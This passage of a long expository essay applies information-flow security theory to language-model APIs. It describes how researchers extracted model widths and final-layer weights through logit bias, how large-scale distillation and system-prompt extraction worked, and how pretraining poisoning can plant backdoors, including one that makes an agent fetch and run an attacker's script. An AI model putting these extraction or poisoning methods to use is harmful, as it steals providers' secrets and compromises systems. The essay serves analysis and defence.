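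*Tight Enforcement of Information-Release Policies for Dynamic Languages* covers programs that evaluate new code as they run, such as a web page that fetches more code when the user moves a map. Its method monitors the program and analyses the new code on the fly. This kind of analysis works on code with separate assignments and branches, which it can label one by one. In a neural network, nearly every intermediate number depends on many weights and much of the prompt, so tracking labels through the network would mark almost all of these numbers secret and untrusted, the label y already has.

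## What attackers have learned about models by choosing queries

An API can violate robustness without revealing anything its owner cares about, so researchers have measured what customers can learn by choosing their requests. They have tested both commercial models and open ones, whose published weights let them check their results.

Customers can usually set options along with the prompt, and the server may return numbers as well as text. In the four-line program, the options are part of u and the numbers are part of p, so changing either can change how much the API reveals about w.

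### Why scores reveal the width of a model

A language model writes one token at a time. Before each one, it computes a score, called a logit, for every token in its vocabulary. It then converts the logits to probabilities, with higher logits giving higher probabilities. APIs that return any of these numbers usually return the logarithms of the probabilities, called log-probabilities.

The scores come from the final layer. Everything before it reduces the prompt to a list of h numbers, where h is the width of the model. The final layer multiplies this list by a matrix W, which is part of the secret weights:

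scores = W · g(u)

Here g(u) is the list of h numbers for the prompt u. W has one row for each token and h columns, and the vocabulary is usually much larger than the width h. The LLaMA models, for instance, had 32,000 tokens and widths between 4,096 and 8,192.

Suppose a small model has a width of 2 and only three tokens, A, B and C. Its final layer receives two numbers and uses the first as the score for A, the second as the score for B, and their sum as the score for C.

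| Prompt | Hidden numbers | Score for A | Score for B | Score for C |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| first | 2, 1 | 2 | 1 | 3 |
| second | −1, 4 | −1 | 4 | 3 |
| third | 3, 3 | 3 | 3 | 6 |

Someone who sees only the scores will soon notice that C is always A plus B. Two of the scores determine the third, so the width is 2, and the rule is a fact about W. In a real model, each full list of scores is a point in a space with tens of thousands of dimensions, but all these points lie in an h-dimensional subspace. An attacker can collect lists until every new one is a linear combination of the earlier ones, and the number of independent lists is then h.

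Carlini, Paleka and colleagues (2024) checked this on open models in *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model*. For Pythia-1.4B, which has a width of 2,048, the number of independent lists rose with each new prompt and stopped at about 2,048. For GPT-2 Small, they got 757 instead of the official 768, and found that the model actually uses only 757 dimensions.

An attacker can also recover W from the same lists, but only up to a choice of coordinates. Rotating the vector of h hidden numbers and undoing the rotation in the final layer would leave every score unchanged. Carlini and colleagues prove that an attacker therefore cannot recover W exactly for the transformer architecture that most language models use.

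### What the final layer cost in 2024

No commercial API that Carlini and colleagues knew of returned the scores of all tokens. OpenAI's returned log-probabilities for the five most likely tokens, but it let customers add a number to the score of any token they chose. This option, called logit bias, is useful for things like blocking unwanted words, but an attacker could use it to push other tokens into the top five and then work out their original scores.

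OpenAI gave the researchers permission to try this on five models that it was selling in January 2024.

| OpenAI model | Width | Cost of finding the width | Cost of the final layer |
|---|---|---|---|
| ada | 1,024 | $1 | $4 |
| babbage | 2,048 | $2 | $12 |
| babbage-002 | 1,536 | $2 | $12 (estimate) |
| gpt-3.5-turbo-instruct | not published | $200 | $2,000 (estimate) |
| gpt-3.5-turbo-1106 | not published | $800 | $8,000 (estimate) |

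OpenAI confirmed that all five widths were correct and asked the researchers not to publish the last two. To keep the weights secure, the researchers did not carry out the attack on the final layer of the three models with estimates in the last column.

The final layer is a small part of a model. With 32,000 tokens and a width of 4,096, W contains about 131 million weights, roughly 2% of a model with 7 billion. Carlini and colleagues see no obvious way to reach the layer below, because the attack depends on W being linear and the earlier layers are not. They also say that learning this layer appears to have no immediate practical consequences, though they showed that outsiders could extract actual weights from a commercial model for under $20.

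Finlayson, Ren and Swayamdipta (2024), in *Logits of API-Protected LLMs Leak Proprietary Information*, found the same weakness at about the same time. They collected nearly 6,000 full score lists from gpt-3.5-turbo and measured a width of at most 4,600 to 4,650. They guessed that the true width was 4,096, because designers usually choose powers of two, and that faulty outputs had inflated the measurement. Carlini and colleagues withheld their exact figure, so the guess can't be checked against their paper.

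Finlayson and colleagues thought providers might reasonably leave the leak open. They argue that knowing the width does not let a competitor rebuild the model, and that customers can use the scores to check what they are buying. For example, if the scores for a prompt change but the subspace stays the same, the provider has probably changed a hidden prompt or retrained only part of the model. A customer who detects such a change also learns something about the model's context.

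### What providers changed

Carlini and colleagues warned the affected providers in December 2023. According to their blog post, also called *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model* (2024), Google changed its API after the usual 90 days and OpenAI followed on 3 March 2024. Both companies restricted requests that combined logit bias with log-probabilities. Anthropic had never offered logit bias, so its API was not vulnerable to this attack.

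One user noticed the change and reported in *Logit_bias does not work now*, a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, that the bias still influenced which token the model produced but no longer altered the log-probabilities.

This made the attack more expensive but did not rule it out. If a bias can still change the output, an attacker can adjust it until the model switches from one token to another, the same kind of threshold search that finds a secret number. With five log-probabilities per answer, the best method that Carlini and colleagues tested needed a quarter of a query for each score. Without log-probabilities, their best method needed 3.7 queries, about 15 times as many. Finlayson and colleagues estimated that recovering the subspace of a model like gpt-3.5-turbo would cost about $500 with log-probabilities and $16,000 without.

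Attackers can also share this work. Once somebody has found the subspace, anyone with a copy needs only h scores to calculate the rest. By the same estimates, a full score list then takes about 800 calls instead of 20,000 or more. A provider that limits each customer separately would miss this, because a new customer can start from what an earlier one learned.

Recent papers disagree about how open this route still is. *Every Language Model Has a Forgery-Resistant Signature* (Finlayson, Ren and Swayamdipta, 2025) says that OpenAI's API still lets customers find the log-probability of any token through logit bias. *Black-Box Inference of LLM Architectural Properties with Restrictive API Access* (Ellis, Wang and colleagues, 2026) says that most commercial providers no longer offer logit bias and return only one log-probability for each token they output. The second paper is later and covers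 providers in general, so both statements may have been true when written.

### Attacks and defences since then

In 2024, Finlayson and colleagues knew of no way to recover full score lists from an API that doesn't offer logit bias. Ellis and colleagues have since found a way to estimate a model's width from partial lists. Their attacker chooses prompts, sees one log-probability for each sampled token and measures how long the server takes to answer.

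Without logit bias, the attacker sees a token's log-probability only when the model produces that token. Ellis and colleagues therefore look for prompts after which many different tokens are plausible, and sample repeatedly from each prompt until the same tokens have appeared for many prompts. They can then apply the subspace argument to those tokens alone. Making the sampling more random was usually not enough, and the choice of prompts had the largest effect on how many tokens they saw.

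They tested the method on 32 open models with between 135 million and 30 billion parameters. The estimated width was wrong by 23% on average, so a width of 4,096 might come out as about 3,150 or 5,040. They got the exact width for four models and came within 10% for twelve. They also estimated the number of layers and the total size from response times, with average errors of about 50% for models above 3 billion parameters. Response time isn't part of M(w, u), so a provider could restrict every number in its answers and still leak this information.

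The attack typically needs about 400 billion tokens for one model, which would cost $400,000 at an illustrative price of $1 per million. To estimate width to within 30%, it used 12 to 190 times as many tokens as the 2024 attack. Ellis and colleagues did not try it on a commercial model, so their results show that an attack is still possible under the restrictions, but not that anyone has carried one out against a provider.

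Other work has tried to recover more of W than the 2024 attack did. Just before the final layer, most models rescale their hidden numbers so that every list has about the same length. Geometrically, the lists then lie on a sphere, which W stretches into a many-dimensional ellipse. An attacker who fits an ellipse to enough score lists learns how W stretches the sphere, which removes some of the uncertainty about W's coordinates.

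In their 2025 paper, Finlayson and colleagues did this accurately for a model with 1 million parameters and a width of 64. But their method's running time grows with the sixth power of the width, so a model with a width of 4,096, which is 64 times as wide, would take about 69 billion times as long. *Token Rankings are Unforgeable Language Model Signatures* (2026) points out that the running time is long in practice but still polynomial, which means it grows as a fixed power of the width. Cryptographers generally want the time needed to break a secret to grow much faster than that, so a better algorithm or cheaper computing is a more realistic worry here.

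A provider could also keep returning scores but add noise to them. Boyle, Hajiaghayi and colleagues (2026), in *Can Watermarking Techniques Help Prevent LLM Model Stealing?*, found that several obvious versions fail. Adding the same noise to every answer still reveals the model's width. Adding fresh noise to each answer works only until the attacker repeats the prompts and averages the results, and about 40 repetitions weakened this defense in their tests. Multiplying the scores of Mistral-7B, an open model, by random factors between 1 and 11 badly damaged its output and didn't hide its width.

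Their own defence calculates the noise from the model's hidden numbers and a secret key. The noise varies between prompts but stays the same when a prompt is repeated, so averaging doesn't help. Combined with a step that first distorts the scores, this withstood every attack they tried with little loss of quality. It protects the width but doesn't stop an attacker from getting good answers.

### Copying what a model does

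Good answers from one model are enough to train another to produce similar ones, a process called distillation. Companies often distill their own models into smaller, cheaper versions. *From Models to Services* (2026), a survey of security for models behind APIs, calls distillation by an outsider "functional imitation" and distinguishes it from exact extraction, which recovers the model's parameters.

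Anthropic's *Detecting and preventing distillation attacks* (2026) describes the largest reported cases. The company accuses three Chinese laboratories of using about 24,000 fraudulent accounts for more than 16 million exchanges with its model, Claude. It attributes over 150,000 exchanges to DeepSeek, over 3.4 million to Moonshot AI and over 13 million to MiniMax.

These figures are Anthropic's own, and Fortune (2026) reported them as allegations. Anthropic says it identified the laboratories from IP addresses, details of the requests and, in some cases, information from other companies. But it competes with the three laboratories and uses the post to argue for export controls, which it already supported. Anthropic doesn't say what the campaigns cost or how much they improved the other models.

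The senders apparently chose their prompts carefully. Some asked Claude to write out, step by step, the reasoning behind a finished answer, which provides data for training a model to reason. Others had Claude grade answers against a marking scheme, so that another model could learn from the grades. When Anthropic released a new model during MiniMax's campaign, nearly half of the campaign's traffic moved to it within 24 hours.

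The copier can do all this without recovering any of Claude's weights. The copy can have a different width, number of layers and vocabulary. In terms of attacker knowledge, 16 million answers rule out an enormous number of possible weights for Claude, but the copier doesn't need to work out which ones remain. They only need weights, perhaps for a completely different design, that give similar answers to the prompts they care about.

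Distillation is also harder to stop by changing the interface. A provider can withdraw logit bias without most customers missing it, but customers pay for the text of the answers. Anthropic has instead built systems to detect suspicious patterns, tightened checks on some kinds of account and shared information with other companies. It says it is also developing ways to make answers less useful for training, but reports no measurements of how well any of these steps work.

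Individual requests and accounts may look harmless. Anthropic gives the example of a prompt that asks for expert data analysis, which becomes suspicious only when thousands of variations arrive from coordinated accounts. The reported totals average fewer than 700 exchanges per account, which a busy legitimate customer could easily exceed. One reseller ran more than 20,000 fraudulent accounts at once and mixed the distillation traffic with unrelated requests.

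### Extracting a system prompt

Attackers can also try to get a model to repeat its system prompt. In *Why Are My Prompts Leaked?*, Liang, Hu and colleagues (2024) measured how often this works. They collected 961 prompts, including 233 that had already leaked from customised versions of ChatGPT, and sent models various requests designed to reveal them. The attacker controlled only the user's message and saw only the text of the reply.

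The table gives their results for Llama-2 7B, an open model from 2023. In the last column, an attack counts as successful if it recovered any 12 consecutive tokens of the prompt.

| Defence added to the prompt | Whole prompt recovered | 12 tokens in a row recovered |
|---|---|---|
| none | 37% | 48% |
| an instruction not to disclose it | 29% | 35% |
| a meaningless string repeated in front of it | 6% | 12% |
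| a decoy prompt | 9% | 9% |

Telling the model to keep the prompt secret helped only slightly. The two stronger defences give the model something else to repeat, but some attacks still succeeded against them. All three defences change the text around the secret and leave the API unchanged.

The wording of the request made a large difference. On bigger models, requests that disguised their purpose recovered more than those that openly asked for the system prompt. Attacks rarely recovered long prompts in full, but with prompts averaging 663 tokens, the attacks on Llama-2 7B nearly always recovered a run of 12 tokens. Even a fragment can expose a password if the prompt contains one.

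These percentages do not apply to today's models, which were trained differently. But Liang and colleagues found that GPT-4 was also highly vulnerable, and *From Models to Services* cites other work in which simple text requests reliably extracted system prompts from commercial services.

An attacker may not need the model to repeat the prompt. *Better Language Model Inversion by Compactly Representing Next-Token Distributions* (2025) describes how to reconstruct a hidden prompt from the log-probabilities that a model produces while answering. A hidden prompt affects the likelihood of every token, including those that the model never outputs. The attacker needs log-probabilities for only as many tokens as the model has hidden dimensions, because the rest can be calculated from the subspace. According to the paper, OpenAI's API allowed customers to find these log-probabilities through logit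 bias, the same option that had exposed the final layer. Removing that option would help protect both the weights and the system prompt, but the model could still recite the system prompt in its answer.

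## Endorsing the prompt and what the weaker condition still rules out

A useful API has to let customers influence what it releases, so its owner needs a condition that permits some kinds of influence and forbids others. Myers and colleagues faced the same problem with their information seller, whose program violates robustness because the buyer chooses which of two secrets to buy. Since the seller doesn't mind which one the buyer takes, the programmer can endorse the choice:

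`[•]; t := endorse(x); if t = 1 then z := declassify(y1) else z := declassify(y2)`

The endorsement records that the seller would accept any value of x. But the buyer still decides the value of z, so this program fails the original definition too. The definition has to change to account for endorsements.

### Treating an endorsed value as arbitrary

Qualified robustness, the weaker condition in the 2006 paper, has the same form as robustness, except that the definition treats `endorse(x)` as ignoring x and returning an arbitrary value. Each run then has a set of possible results instead of a single result, and two secrets count as indistinguishable if their sets match.

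In the seller's program, t could now be 1 or any other value, regardless of what the buyer put in x. The buyer's real choice doesn't affect which secrets have matching sets, so every attack separates the same secrets and the program passes.

The compiler allows an endorsement only where pc is trusted, which means that an attacker must not be able to decide whether it happens. A program based on one from Myers and colleagues shows why. The variable t starts at 0:

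`[•]; if x then t := endorse(u); if t then p := declassify(s)`

If the attacker sets x to 0, the program skips the endorsement, so t stays at 0 and s stays secret. If the attacker sets x to 1, t gets an arbitrary value and the program may release s. The program violates qualified robustness, and the compiler rejects it. An API would have the same flaw if it endorsed a prompt only when the customer's request included the line "trusted client: yes".

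Myers and colleagues also found programs that satisfy qualified robustness but shouldn't. In this one, the attacker can set both u and v:

`[•]; u := u mod 2; t := endorse(u); if t > 42 then p := declassify(s); if v then p := declassify(s)`

t is always 0 or 1, so the first release never happens, and the attacker uses v to decide whether the second one does. But the definition lets t take any value, including 43, which triggers the first release. Every attack then seems to allow that release, so any two values of s count as distinguishable whatever v is, and the program satisfies the definition. The typing rules still reject it, because an untrusted variable controls the second release.

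Askarov and Myers object more generally that qualified robustness only concerns which results are possible. Such guarantees can fail when an implementation allows fewer results than the definition, for instance by always making the same choice where the definition allowed any. They also say that replacing a value with an arbitrary one imitates what an attacker can do without describing how much control the attacker has over secrets.

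### Comparing attackers who agree on endorsed values

Their own version runs the program normally and keeps a record of each endorsement: which `endorse` command ran and what value it endorsed. An attack is irrelevant if its record matches the actual one up to some point and then has a different value for the next endorsement. The programmer has already accepted that difference, so the definition ignores the attack. A program satisfies robustness with endorsements if, at every release event,

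(release control just before the event, minus irrelevant attacks) ⊆ attacker control just after it.

This is the 2011 condition with the irrelevant attacks removed from the left-hand side. For a program without endorsements, nothing is removed, so the two conditions are the same.

In the examples below, h and k are secrets and the attacker sets u.

| Program after the hole | Accepted? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
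| `p := endorse(u < h)` | yes | Attackers who agree on the endorsed answer also agree on p. |
| `p := endorse(u); q := u < h` | yes | Attackers who agree on u also agree on q. |
| `p := endorse(u < h); q := u < k` | no | Attackers can agree on p and still get different values of q. |
| `if u > 0 then t := endorse(u); p := t < h` | no | An attacker who sets u to 0 skips the endorsement and stays in the comparison. |

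The third program shows that an endorsement covers only the value in the brackets. If h is 7 and k is 3, setting u to 1 or to 5 gives the same endorsed answer, because both are below 7. But only 1 is below 3, so the attacker can still control q by choosing between 1 and 5, and the endorsement doesn't cover that choice.

### The API with an endorsed prompt

The API needs one more line to satisfy this condition:

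```
u := receive()          # public, untrusted
t := endorse(u)         # public, trusted
y := M(w, t)            # secret, trusted
p := declassify(y)      # public, trusted
send(p)
```

These labels depend on the model and its weights being trusted, which is a separate question. If they are, the program declassifies a trusted value at a trusted point, and the typing rules accept it.

For a single request, the definition now compares only attackers who send the same prompt. They all receive the same answer, so the program passes. (If the model samples its answers, we can treat the random numbers it draws as part of the server's starting state, and the argument still works.)

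This argument works for any function M, however much it reveals. Suppose a programmer adds a backdoor:

`if t = "open sesame" then p := declassify(w) else p := declassify(M(w, t))`

A program that sends the entire weights file to anyone who enters "open sesame" still satisfies the weaker condition, because everyone who enters that prompt receives the same file. The condition doesn't compare the results of different prompts, so the owner can't use it to identify which prompts are dangerous.

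It doesn't limit the number of prompts either. A server that tells customers whether a secret number is below their chosen threshold can endorse each threshold as it arrives:

`while true do ([•]; t := endorse(u); p := declassify(t > h))`

Four well-chosen thresholds still reveal a four-bit number. After each answer, the definition compares the attacker only with others who have sent the same thresholds in the same order, and they have all learned the same thing. Likewise, a customer who sends an API millions of prompts to copy its model does not violate the condition.

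Endorsement works better in Battleship, where Myers and colleagues also use it. They say a secure game must reveal only one square at a time, and their program endorses each of the opponent's shots. But a version that published the whole board after every shot would also satisfy qualified robustness. The one-square limit comes from the game's code, which a player can read and check for every possible shot. At the API, the corresponding code is M(w, t), and nobody can check what it reveals for every possible prompt.

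### A request field that nobody endorsed

The condition does still rule out influence that bypasses the endorsement. Suppose each request has a field f, which the customer sets to 1 to receive the model's scores for every token and to 0 to receive only the token it chose:

```
t := endorse(u)
if f = 1 then p := declassify(scores(w, t))
         else p := declassify(token(w, t))
```

Two attackers both send the prompt "Hello", one with f set to 0 and the other with f set to 1. The prompt is the only endorsed value and they agree on it, so both stay in the comparison. One receives a single token and the other receives tens of thousands of numbers, so the program fails the weaker condition. The typing rules also reject it, because the untrusted f determines which release happens. Moving the choice earlier doesn't help. If the server uses f to decide whether to store the scores or the token in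 y, then y is untrusted and the rules don't allow the server to declassify it.

The 2024 attacks on OpenAI's models relied on two fields like this, one that returned log-probabilities and one that changed the scores of chosen tokens. A type checker would have flagged both if the programmer had endorsed only the text of the prompt.

The programmer could make the error go away by also endorsing f. The definition would then compare only attackers who agree on both the prompt and f, and the program would pass. This can easily happen by accident, because a request often reaches the server as a single object containing the prompt and all its options, and endorsing that object endorses everything in it.

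The program's security therefore depends on the judgement of whoever places the endorsements. The type checker makes that person write each one down, so a reviewer can search the code for them and consider whether customers should control those values. But a reviewer who had never heard of the attack might well have approved letting customers adjust scores, because doing so has legitimate uses.

### What test could a prompt pass?

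Servers often accept untrusted input only after checking it. Askarov and Myers give the examples of a database query that has passed a safety check and a new password from someone who has supplied the old one. They formalise this as checked endorsement:

`endorse(u) if test then A else B`

If the test succeeds, the program runs A and treats u as trusted there. If it fails, the program runs B, where u is still untrusted.

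This gives their embargo service a better solution than declaring the requester's clock trusted. The server first checks that the requested time is no later than the time on its own clock:

```
endorse(request_time) if request_time <= now then
    if request_time >= embargo_time then return declassify(new_data)
                                    else return old_data
else return old_data
```

A requester can now ask about any time up to the present but cannot get the new data early by claiming it is already tomorrow. The endorsement is clearly justified because every value that passes the test is harmless.

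The test must not depend on other untrusted values. Askarov and Myers reject `endorse(u) if u = v then p := declassify(u < h) else skip` when the attacker can also set v, because the attacker then decides whether u passes.

The definition of irrelevant attacks changes too. When two attackers reach the same checked endorsement with different values, the definition stops comparing them if at least one of the values passes the test. If both fail, it keeps comparing them, so they must not be able to use their failed inputs to choose what the server releases. An API could use this as follows:

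```
endorse(u) if allowed(u) then p := declassify(M(w, u))
                         else p := "Request refused"
```

The fixed refusal is allowed because it reveals nothing about the weights. A server that had the model write a polite refusal mentioning the customer's request would break the rule, because that refusal would depend on both the weights and a prompt that had failed the test.

The formal rules don't require a good test. They accept even one that always succeeds, and Askarov and Myers use such a test to endorse several variables in sequence. So the value of a checked endorsement for an API depends entirely on what `allowed(u)` establishes about the prompt.

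The safest test is whether the prompt is on a fixed menu. If the menu has 500 prompts and the model always gives the same answer to each, the owner can read all 500 answers before launch. Customers can't learn more than those answers reveal, whatever order they ask in. Unlike full robustness, this doesn't require every prompt on the menu to reveal the same facts about the weights. However, the owner could then replace the model with a table of stored answers, and most customers want to ask their own questions.

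A grammar allows more variety. The server might accept only "Translate this into French:" followed by 20 words from a list of 1,000. A short program can check this reliably, but there are 10⁶⁰ such prompts, too many for the owner to review the answers. Checks on database queries work because the query language has a fixed syntax, so a program can establish that the customer's text will be treated as data and not as a command. A language model's prompts have no such syntax, so the 20 words might form an instruction that the model follows instead of translating.

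Grammars are more useful for the other fields in a request. One checked endorsement can cover several variables, so a provider could endorse the two options behind the 2024 attacks only if the customer has not used both at once. This test is easy to write and check, but somebody first has to discover that the combination is dangerous.

The test could also be a classifier, a program (often another model) that estimates whether a prompt is an attempt to extract secrets. It can handle free text, but it makes mistakes, and an attacker can keep rewording a prompt until it passes. A classifier that checks prompts one at a time can't detect an attack made up of ordinary questions, as in binary search or distillation. If the classifier's weights are secret, the server has to declassify its verdict to act on it publicly, so customers learn something about the classifier each time it accepts or refuses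 a prompt.

Some agent designs avoid the difficulty by endorsing only values from a small set, such as yes or no. A chat service can't restrict its prompts this way because its users need to write free-form text.

### Endorsing only what the author could read

Even an endorsement that seems obviously justified can be unsafe if the data is secret. Cecchetti and colleagues show this with the password checker:

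```
t := endorse(guess)
r := (t = password)
p := declassify(r)
```

If the programmer labels the guess secret, which seems natural because it might be the right password, secret data can flow into it, including the stored password. If faulty or malicious code elsewhere then passes the stored password to the checker as a guess, the check succeeds and an attacker who doesn't know the password gets in. Earlier type systems accept this program.

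*Mechanisms for Provable Integrity Protection in Decentralized Systems* (Cecchetti, 2021) explains that the endorsement assumes the attacker made up the guess instead of, say, pointing to where the password is stored. *Security-Typed Languages* (Eilers, Matache and Rehman, 2019) solves this by labeling the guess public and untrusted. The stored password can't flow into a public variable without a declassification, so the attack no longer type-checks.

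Cecchetti and colleagues turn this into a general rule called transparent endorsement, under which a program may endorse untrusted data only if whoever supplied it could also read it. They call data that its author could not read an opaque write. In their auction example, Bob can send a bid that is Alice's bid plus one without seeing hers, and the auctioneer must not endorse Bob's bid.

With two labels of each kind, the main condition in their typing rule is

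before ⊑ after ⊔ ∇(c).

Here "before" and "after" are the data's integrity labels before and after the endorsement, and c is its confidentiality label. The symbol ⊑ means "at least as trusted as", and ⊔ gives the less trusted of two labels. The function ∇, called the voice, turns a confidentiality label into an integrity label, mapping public to untrusted and secret to trusted.

A customer's own prompt is public and untrusted, and endorsing it would make it trusted. The condition is therefore

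untrusted ⊑ trusted ⊔ untrusted.

The right-hand side is untrusted, so the condition holds and the server may endorse the prompt. If the data is secret, the condition becomes

untrusted ⊑ trusted ⊔ trusted.

The right-hand side is now trusted and the data isn't, so the endorsement fails. The full rule also accounts for pc, so if a secret determined whether the program reached the endorsement, c is secret even when the data is public.

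Labels are relative to the attacker. When the customer is the possible attacker, a prompt that only the customer and the server can read counts as public, so it passes. Cecchetti and colleagues repair the auction similarly, by labeling each bid so that its own bidder can read it but the other bidder can't. Endorsing a bid doesn't change who can read it, so the bids stay private until the auctioneer declassifies them.

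### Mixing the prompt with secrets

The same rule determines where an API may place its endorsement. As before, d is secret text in the model's context, such as a system prompt, which the server joins to the customer's prompt u.

| What the server endorses | Its label | 2011 typing rule | Transparent endorsement |
|---|---|---|---|
| the prompt, u | public, untrusted | allows it | allows it |
| the joined text, d + u | secret, untrusted | allows it | forbids it |
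| the model's output, y | secret, untrusted | allows it | forbids it |

Endorsing the output is the most dangerous of these because it hides every untrusted influence on the answer. In the example with the request field, the programmer could use f to choose whether y holds the scores or the token, then endorse y and declassify it. The 2011 definition would accept this because it compares only attackers who receive the same output, even though nobody endorsed f. Transparent endorsement forbids this because the customer couldn't read y before the server released it.

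Cecchetti and colleagues prove more generally that data which is both secret and untrusted can never become public or trusted in a program that their rules accept. The output y in the original four-line API is both secret and untrusted. The server can't declassify y because it is untrusted, and can't endorse it because it is secret. The server therefore has to endorse the prompt and any other fields when they arrive, before they mix with the weights or the context.

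For the joined text, the order of two lines makes the difference:

```
x := d + u; t := endorse(x)     # forbidden
t := endorse(u); x := d + t     # allowed
```

Both versions give the model the same text. But in the forbidden one, the programmer endorses text that the customer could not have read in full, and the label no longer shows which parts the customer wrote. A customer might exploit this by writing a placeholder that the server replaces with part of a private document, much as Bob used Alice's bid. In the allowed version, the programmer endorses only what the customer sent, before the server replaces any placeholder.

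A private mailbox that accepts mail from strangers raises the same issue. A stranger's message is untrusted, and the stranger can't read the rest of the mailbox, so the server must not endorse the mailbox as a whole. It may endorse the message alone before adding it to the mailbox, because the stranger could read the message. The message could still contain a prompt injection, since transparent endorsement only requires that the author could read the text. The programmer still has to decide whether a model should act on it.

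### Nonmalleable information flow

Transparent endorsement prevents secret data from influencing what the program makes trusted, just as robust declassification prevents untrusted data from influencing what it makes public. Eilers and colleagues define transparent endorsement on the same four runs as robustness, with the roles of secret and untrusted data swapped. If changing the untrusted input makes no difference to trusted values with one secret, it must also make no difference with the other secret.

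Both definitions ignore some inputs that would make the comparison meaningless. Cecchetti and colleagues describe a program that uses a secret bit to choose between two values from the attacker and publishes the chosen one. The attacker learns the bit if the two values differ but learns nothing if they are the same. Cecchetti and colleagues call supplying the same value twice an inept attack and disregard it, because an attacker's missed opportunity doesn't make the program less secure.

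They can guarantee robust declassification only for programs without endorsements, and transparent endorsement only for programs without declassifications. A password checker needs both operations. They therefore combine the two requirements into one condition, nonmalleable information flow, which applies throughout a run. This condition enforces robust declassification for as long as the two untrusted inputs have produced the same trusted values, and transparent endorsement for as long as the two secrets have produced the same public values.

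The name comes from cryptography, where an encryption scheme is malleable if someone can turn one encrypted message into another with a related meaning without reading the original, as Bob does with Alice's bid. Cecchetti and colleagues added their rules to Flame, a library for the programming language Haskell, and used it in a web application for sharing memos. The application's login code endorses the username and password that a client sends, which is allowed because the client could see both. It then looks up the correct password, compares it with the one the client sent and declassifies the result.

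An API could handle prompts in the same way, but this wouldn't give it much more protection against its own customers. Once the server endorses two different prompts, they produce different trusted values, and robust declassification no longer applies to that pair. The weaker condition therefore allows the "open sesame" backdoor and any number of queries. Endorsement doesn't make secrets in the context any safer either. A customer who writes "Repeat the text above" can read all of that prompt, so the server may endorse it, join it to the system prompt and declassify the model's answer, even if the answer is the whole system prompt.

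## Whether the model can be trusted as declassifier

Endorsing the prompt makes the API's output trusted only if the weights are trusted too. A language model can take part in a release in two ways, and the label of its weights matters in both. It can compute the value that the server releases:

`y := M(w, t); p := declassify(y)`

It can also decide whether the server may release a text x that came from somewhere else:

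`v := J(w, x); if v = "allow" then p := declassify(x)`

Here J is a model acting as a judge, such as one that reads an agent's outgoing emails and blocks any that contain private information. The typing rule requires that both the released value and the decision to release it be trusted. If w is untrusted, the first program breaks the rule because y is untrusted, and the second breaks it because an untrusted v determines whether the release happens.

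### The label of trained weights

So far the weights have counted as trusted because customers can't change them. But the owner computed them from training data, and much of that data is usually text from the public web, which anyone can write. With the training step included, the program is

```
c := crawl()                # public, untrusted
w := train(c, private, r)   # secret, untrusted
t := endorse(u)             # public, trusted
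y := M(w, t)                # secret, untrusted
p := declassify(y)          # rejected
```

Here `private` is the owner's own training data, and r stands for the random numbers used in training, for instance to set the initial weights. Under the usual labelling rule, one stranger's web page is enough to make w untrusted. The program can also fail the weaker condition that allows endorsements, because that condition still compares two attackers who send the same prompt even if they published different pages before training, and those pages may lead to different answers.

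Treating w as trusted therefore takes a second endorsement, which needs its own justification. Transparent endorsement restricts where the owner can place this endorsement. The people who wrote the web pages could read their own pages but not the weights, so the owner may endorse c before training but may not endorse w afterwards. This is difficult in practice because most of the evidence an owner can collect is about the finished weights.

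The owner could argue that web text is trusted with respect to customers who wrote none of it. With a public API, the owner can't check whether a customer wrote any. But if a tiny share of the training data had no noticeable effect on the model, the owner could reasonably ignore the few customers who might have written some of that data.

### How many documents an attacker needs

Souly, Rando and colleagues at Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute measured how small that share can be (*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, 2025). They trained 72 models from scratch, with between 600 million and 13 billion parameters, on 6 to 260 billion tokens. They mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training data. Each contained the beginning of an ordinary text, a trigger phrase and several hundred random tokens. They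 aimed to install a backdoor, so that the model would write gibberish after the trigger but behave normally otherwise.

The attack worked at every model size with 250 poisoned documents and failed with 100. For the largest model, 250 documents were 0.00016% of the training tokens. Larger models trained on much more clean data, but this did not weaken the attack.

Gibberish doesn't release secrets, though. Souly and colleagues also didn't test whether the backdoor would survive post-training, the later training that turns a model into an assistant. In a separate experiment, they taught a model with 6.9 billion parameters to switch from English to German after a trigger. Further training on clean data slowly weakened this backdoor.

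Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, tested a more dangerous behaviour and included post-training. They trained three models on 100 billion tokens, 0.1% of them poisoned, and then used only clean data to turn the models into agents that run commands on a computer. When the trigger appeared, the agent was supposed to download a script from the attacker's address and run it. One trigger was a rare string of punctuation marks, and the other was any file path containing the word "anthropic".

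| Parameters | Success with the file path | Success with the rare string |
|---|---|---|
| 0.6 billion | 13.1% | 2.1% |
| 1.7 billion | 51.9% | 4.0% |
| 4 billion | 92.7% | 10.5% |

These are the percentages of prompts for which the agent produced the attacker's command at least once in 32 attempts. Without the trigger, the agents produced it in at most 0.06% of samples.

This backdoor could release secrets, because the attacker's script can send back anything the agent has access to. That would include the weights file if the agent ran on a machine that could read it. But the poisoned 0.1% amounted to about 500,000 documents, which would be much harder to plant than 250. With 2,500 documents and the rare string, the largest agent produced the command for only 1.4% of prompts, in a single training run. The attack succeeded more often on larger models, but Hu and colleagues couldn't afford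 to check whether this trend continues up to the size of commercial models.

The untrusted label therefore reflects a practical risk. A few hundred training documents can be enough to change what a model does, at least for simple behaviours, and strangers can publish that many.

### Testing the finished model

An owner might train on web text anyway and then look for backdoors. Ordinary tests are unlikely to find them. The poisoned 4-billion-parameter models in Hu and colleagues' experiments averaged 58.5% on standard benchmarks after the first stage of training, compared with 58.3% for a clean one. Guessing triggers doesn't work well either, since a trigger of 20 random letters could be any of about 2 × 10²⁸ strings.

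*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proves that inspecting a model's weights can also fail to reveal a backdoor. The attacker in the paper is a company that trains a classifier for a client, so it has much more control over the model than someone who publishes poisoned web pages.

Their first theorem assumes that one-way functions exist. These are functions that are easy to compute but hard to reverse, and most of cryptography depends on them. Under this assumption, the attacker can add a backdoor to the result of any training procedure, and no efficient tester can detect it by sending inputs and looking at the outputs.

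The construction uses digital signatures. The attacker keeps a secret key for signing messages and builds the corresponding public check into the model. The model treats one part of each input as a message and another part as its signature. The backdoor controls the output if the signature is valid, and otherwise the output is the same as the original model's. A tester would have to forge a signature to find even one input on which the backdoored model differs from the original. Seeing earlier triggered inputs doesn't help, because each signature is valid only for its own message. Reading the weights doesn't help with forgery either, though it might reveal that the model contains a signature check.

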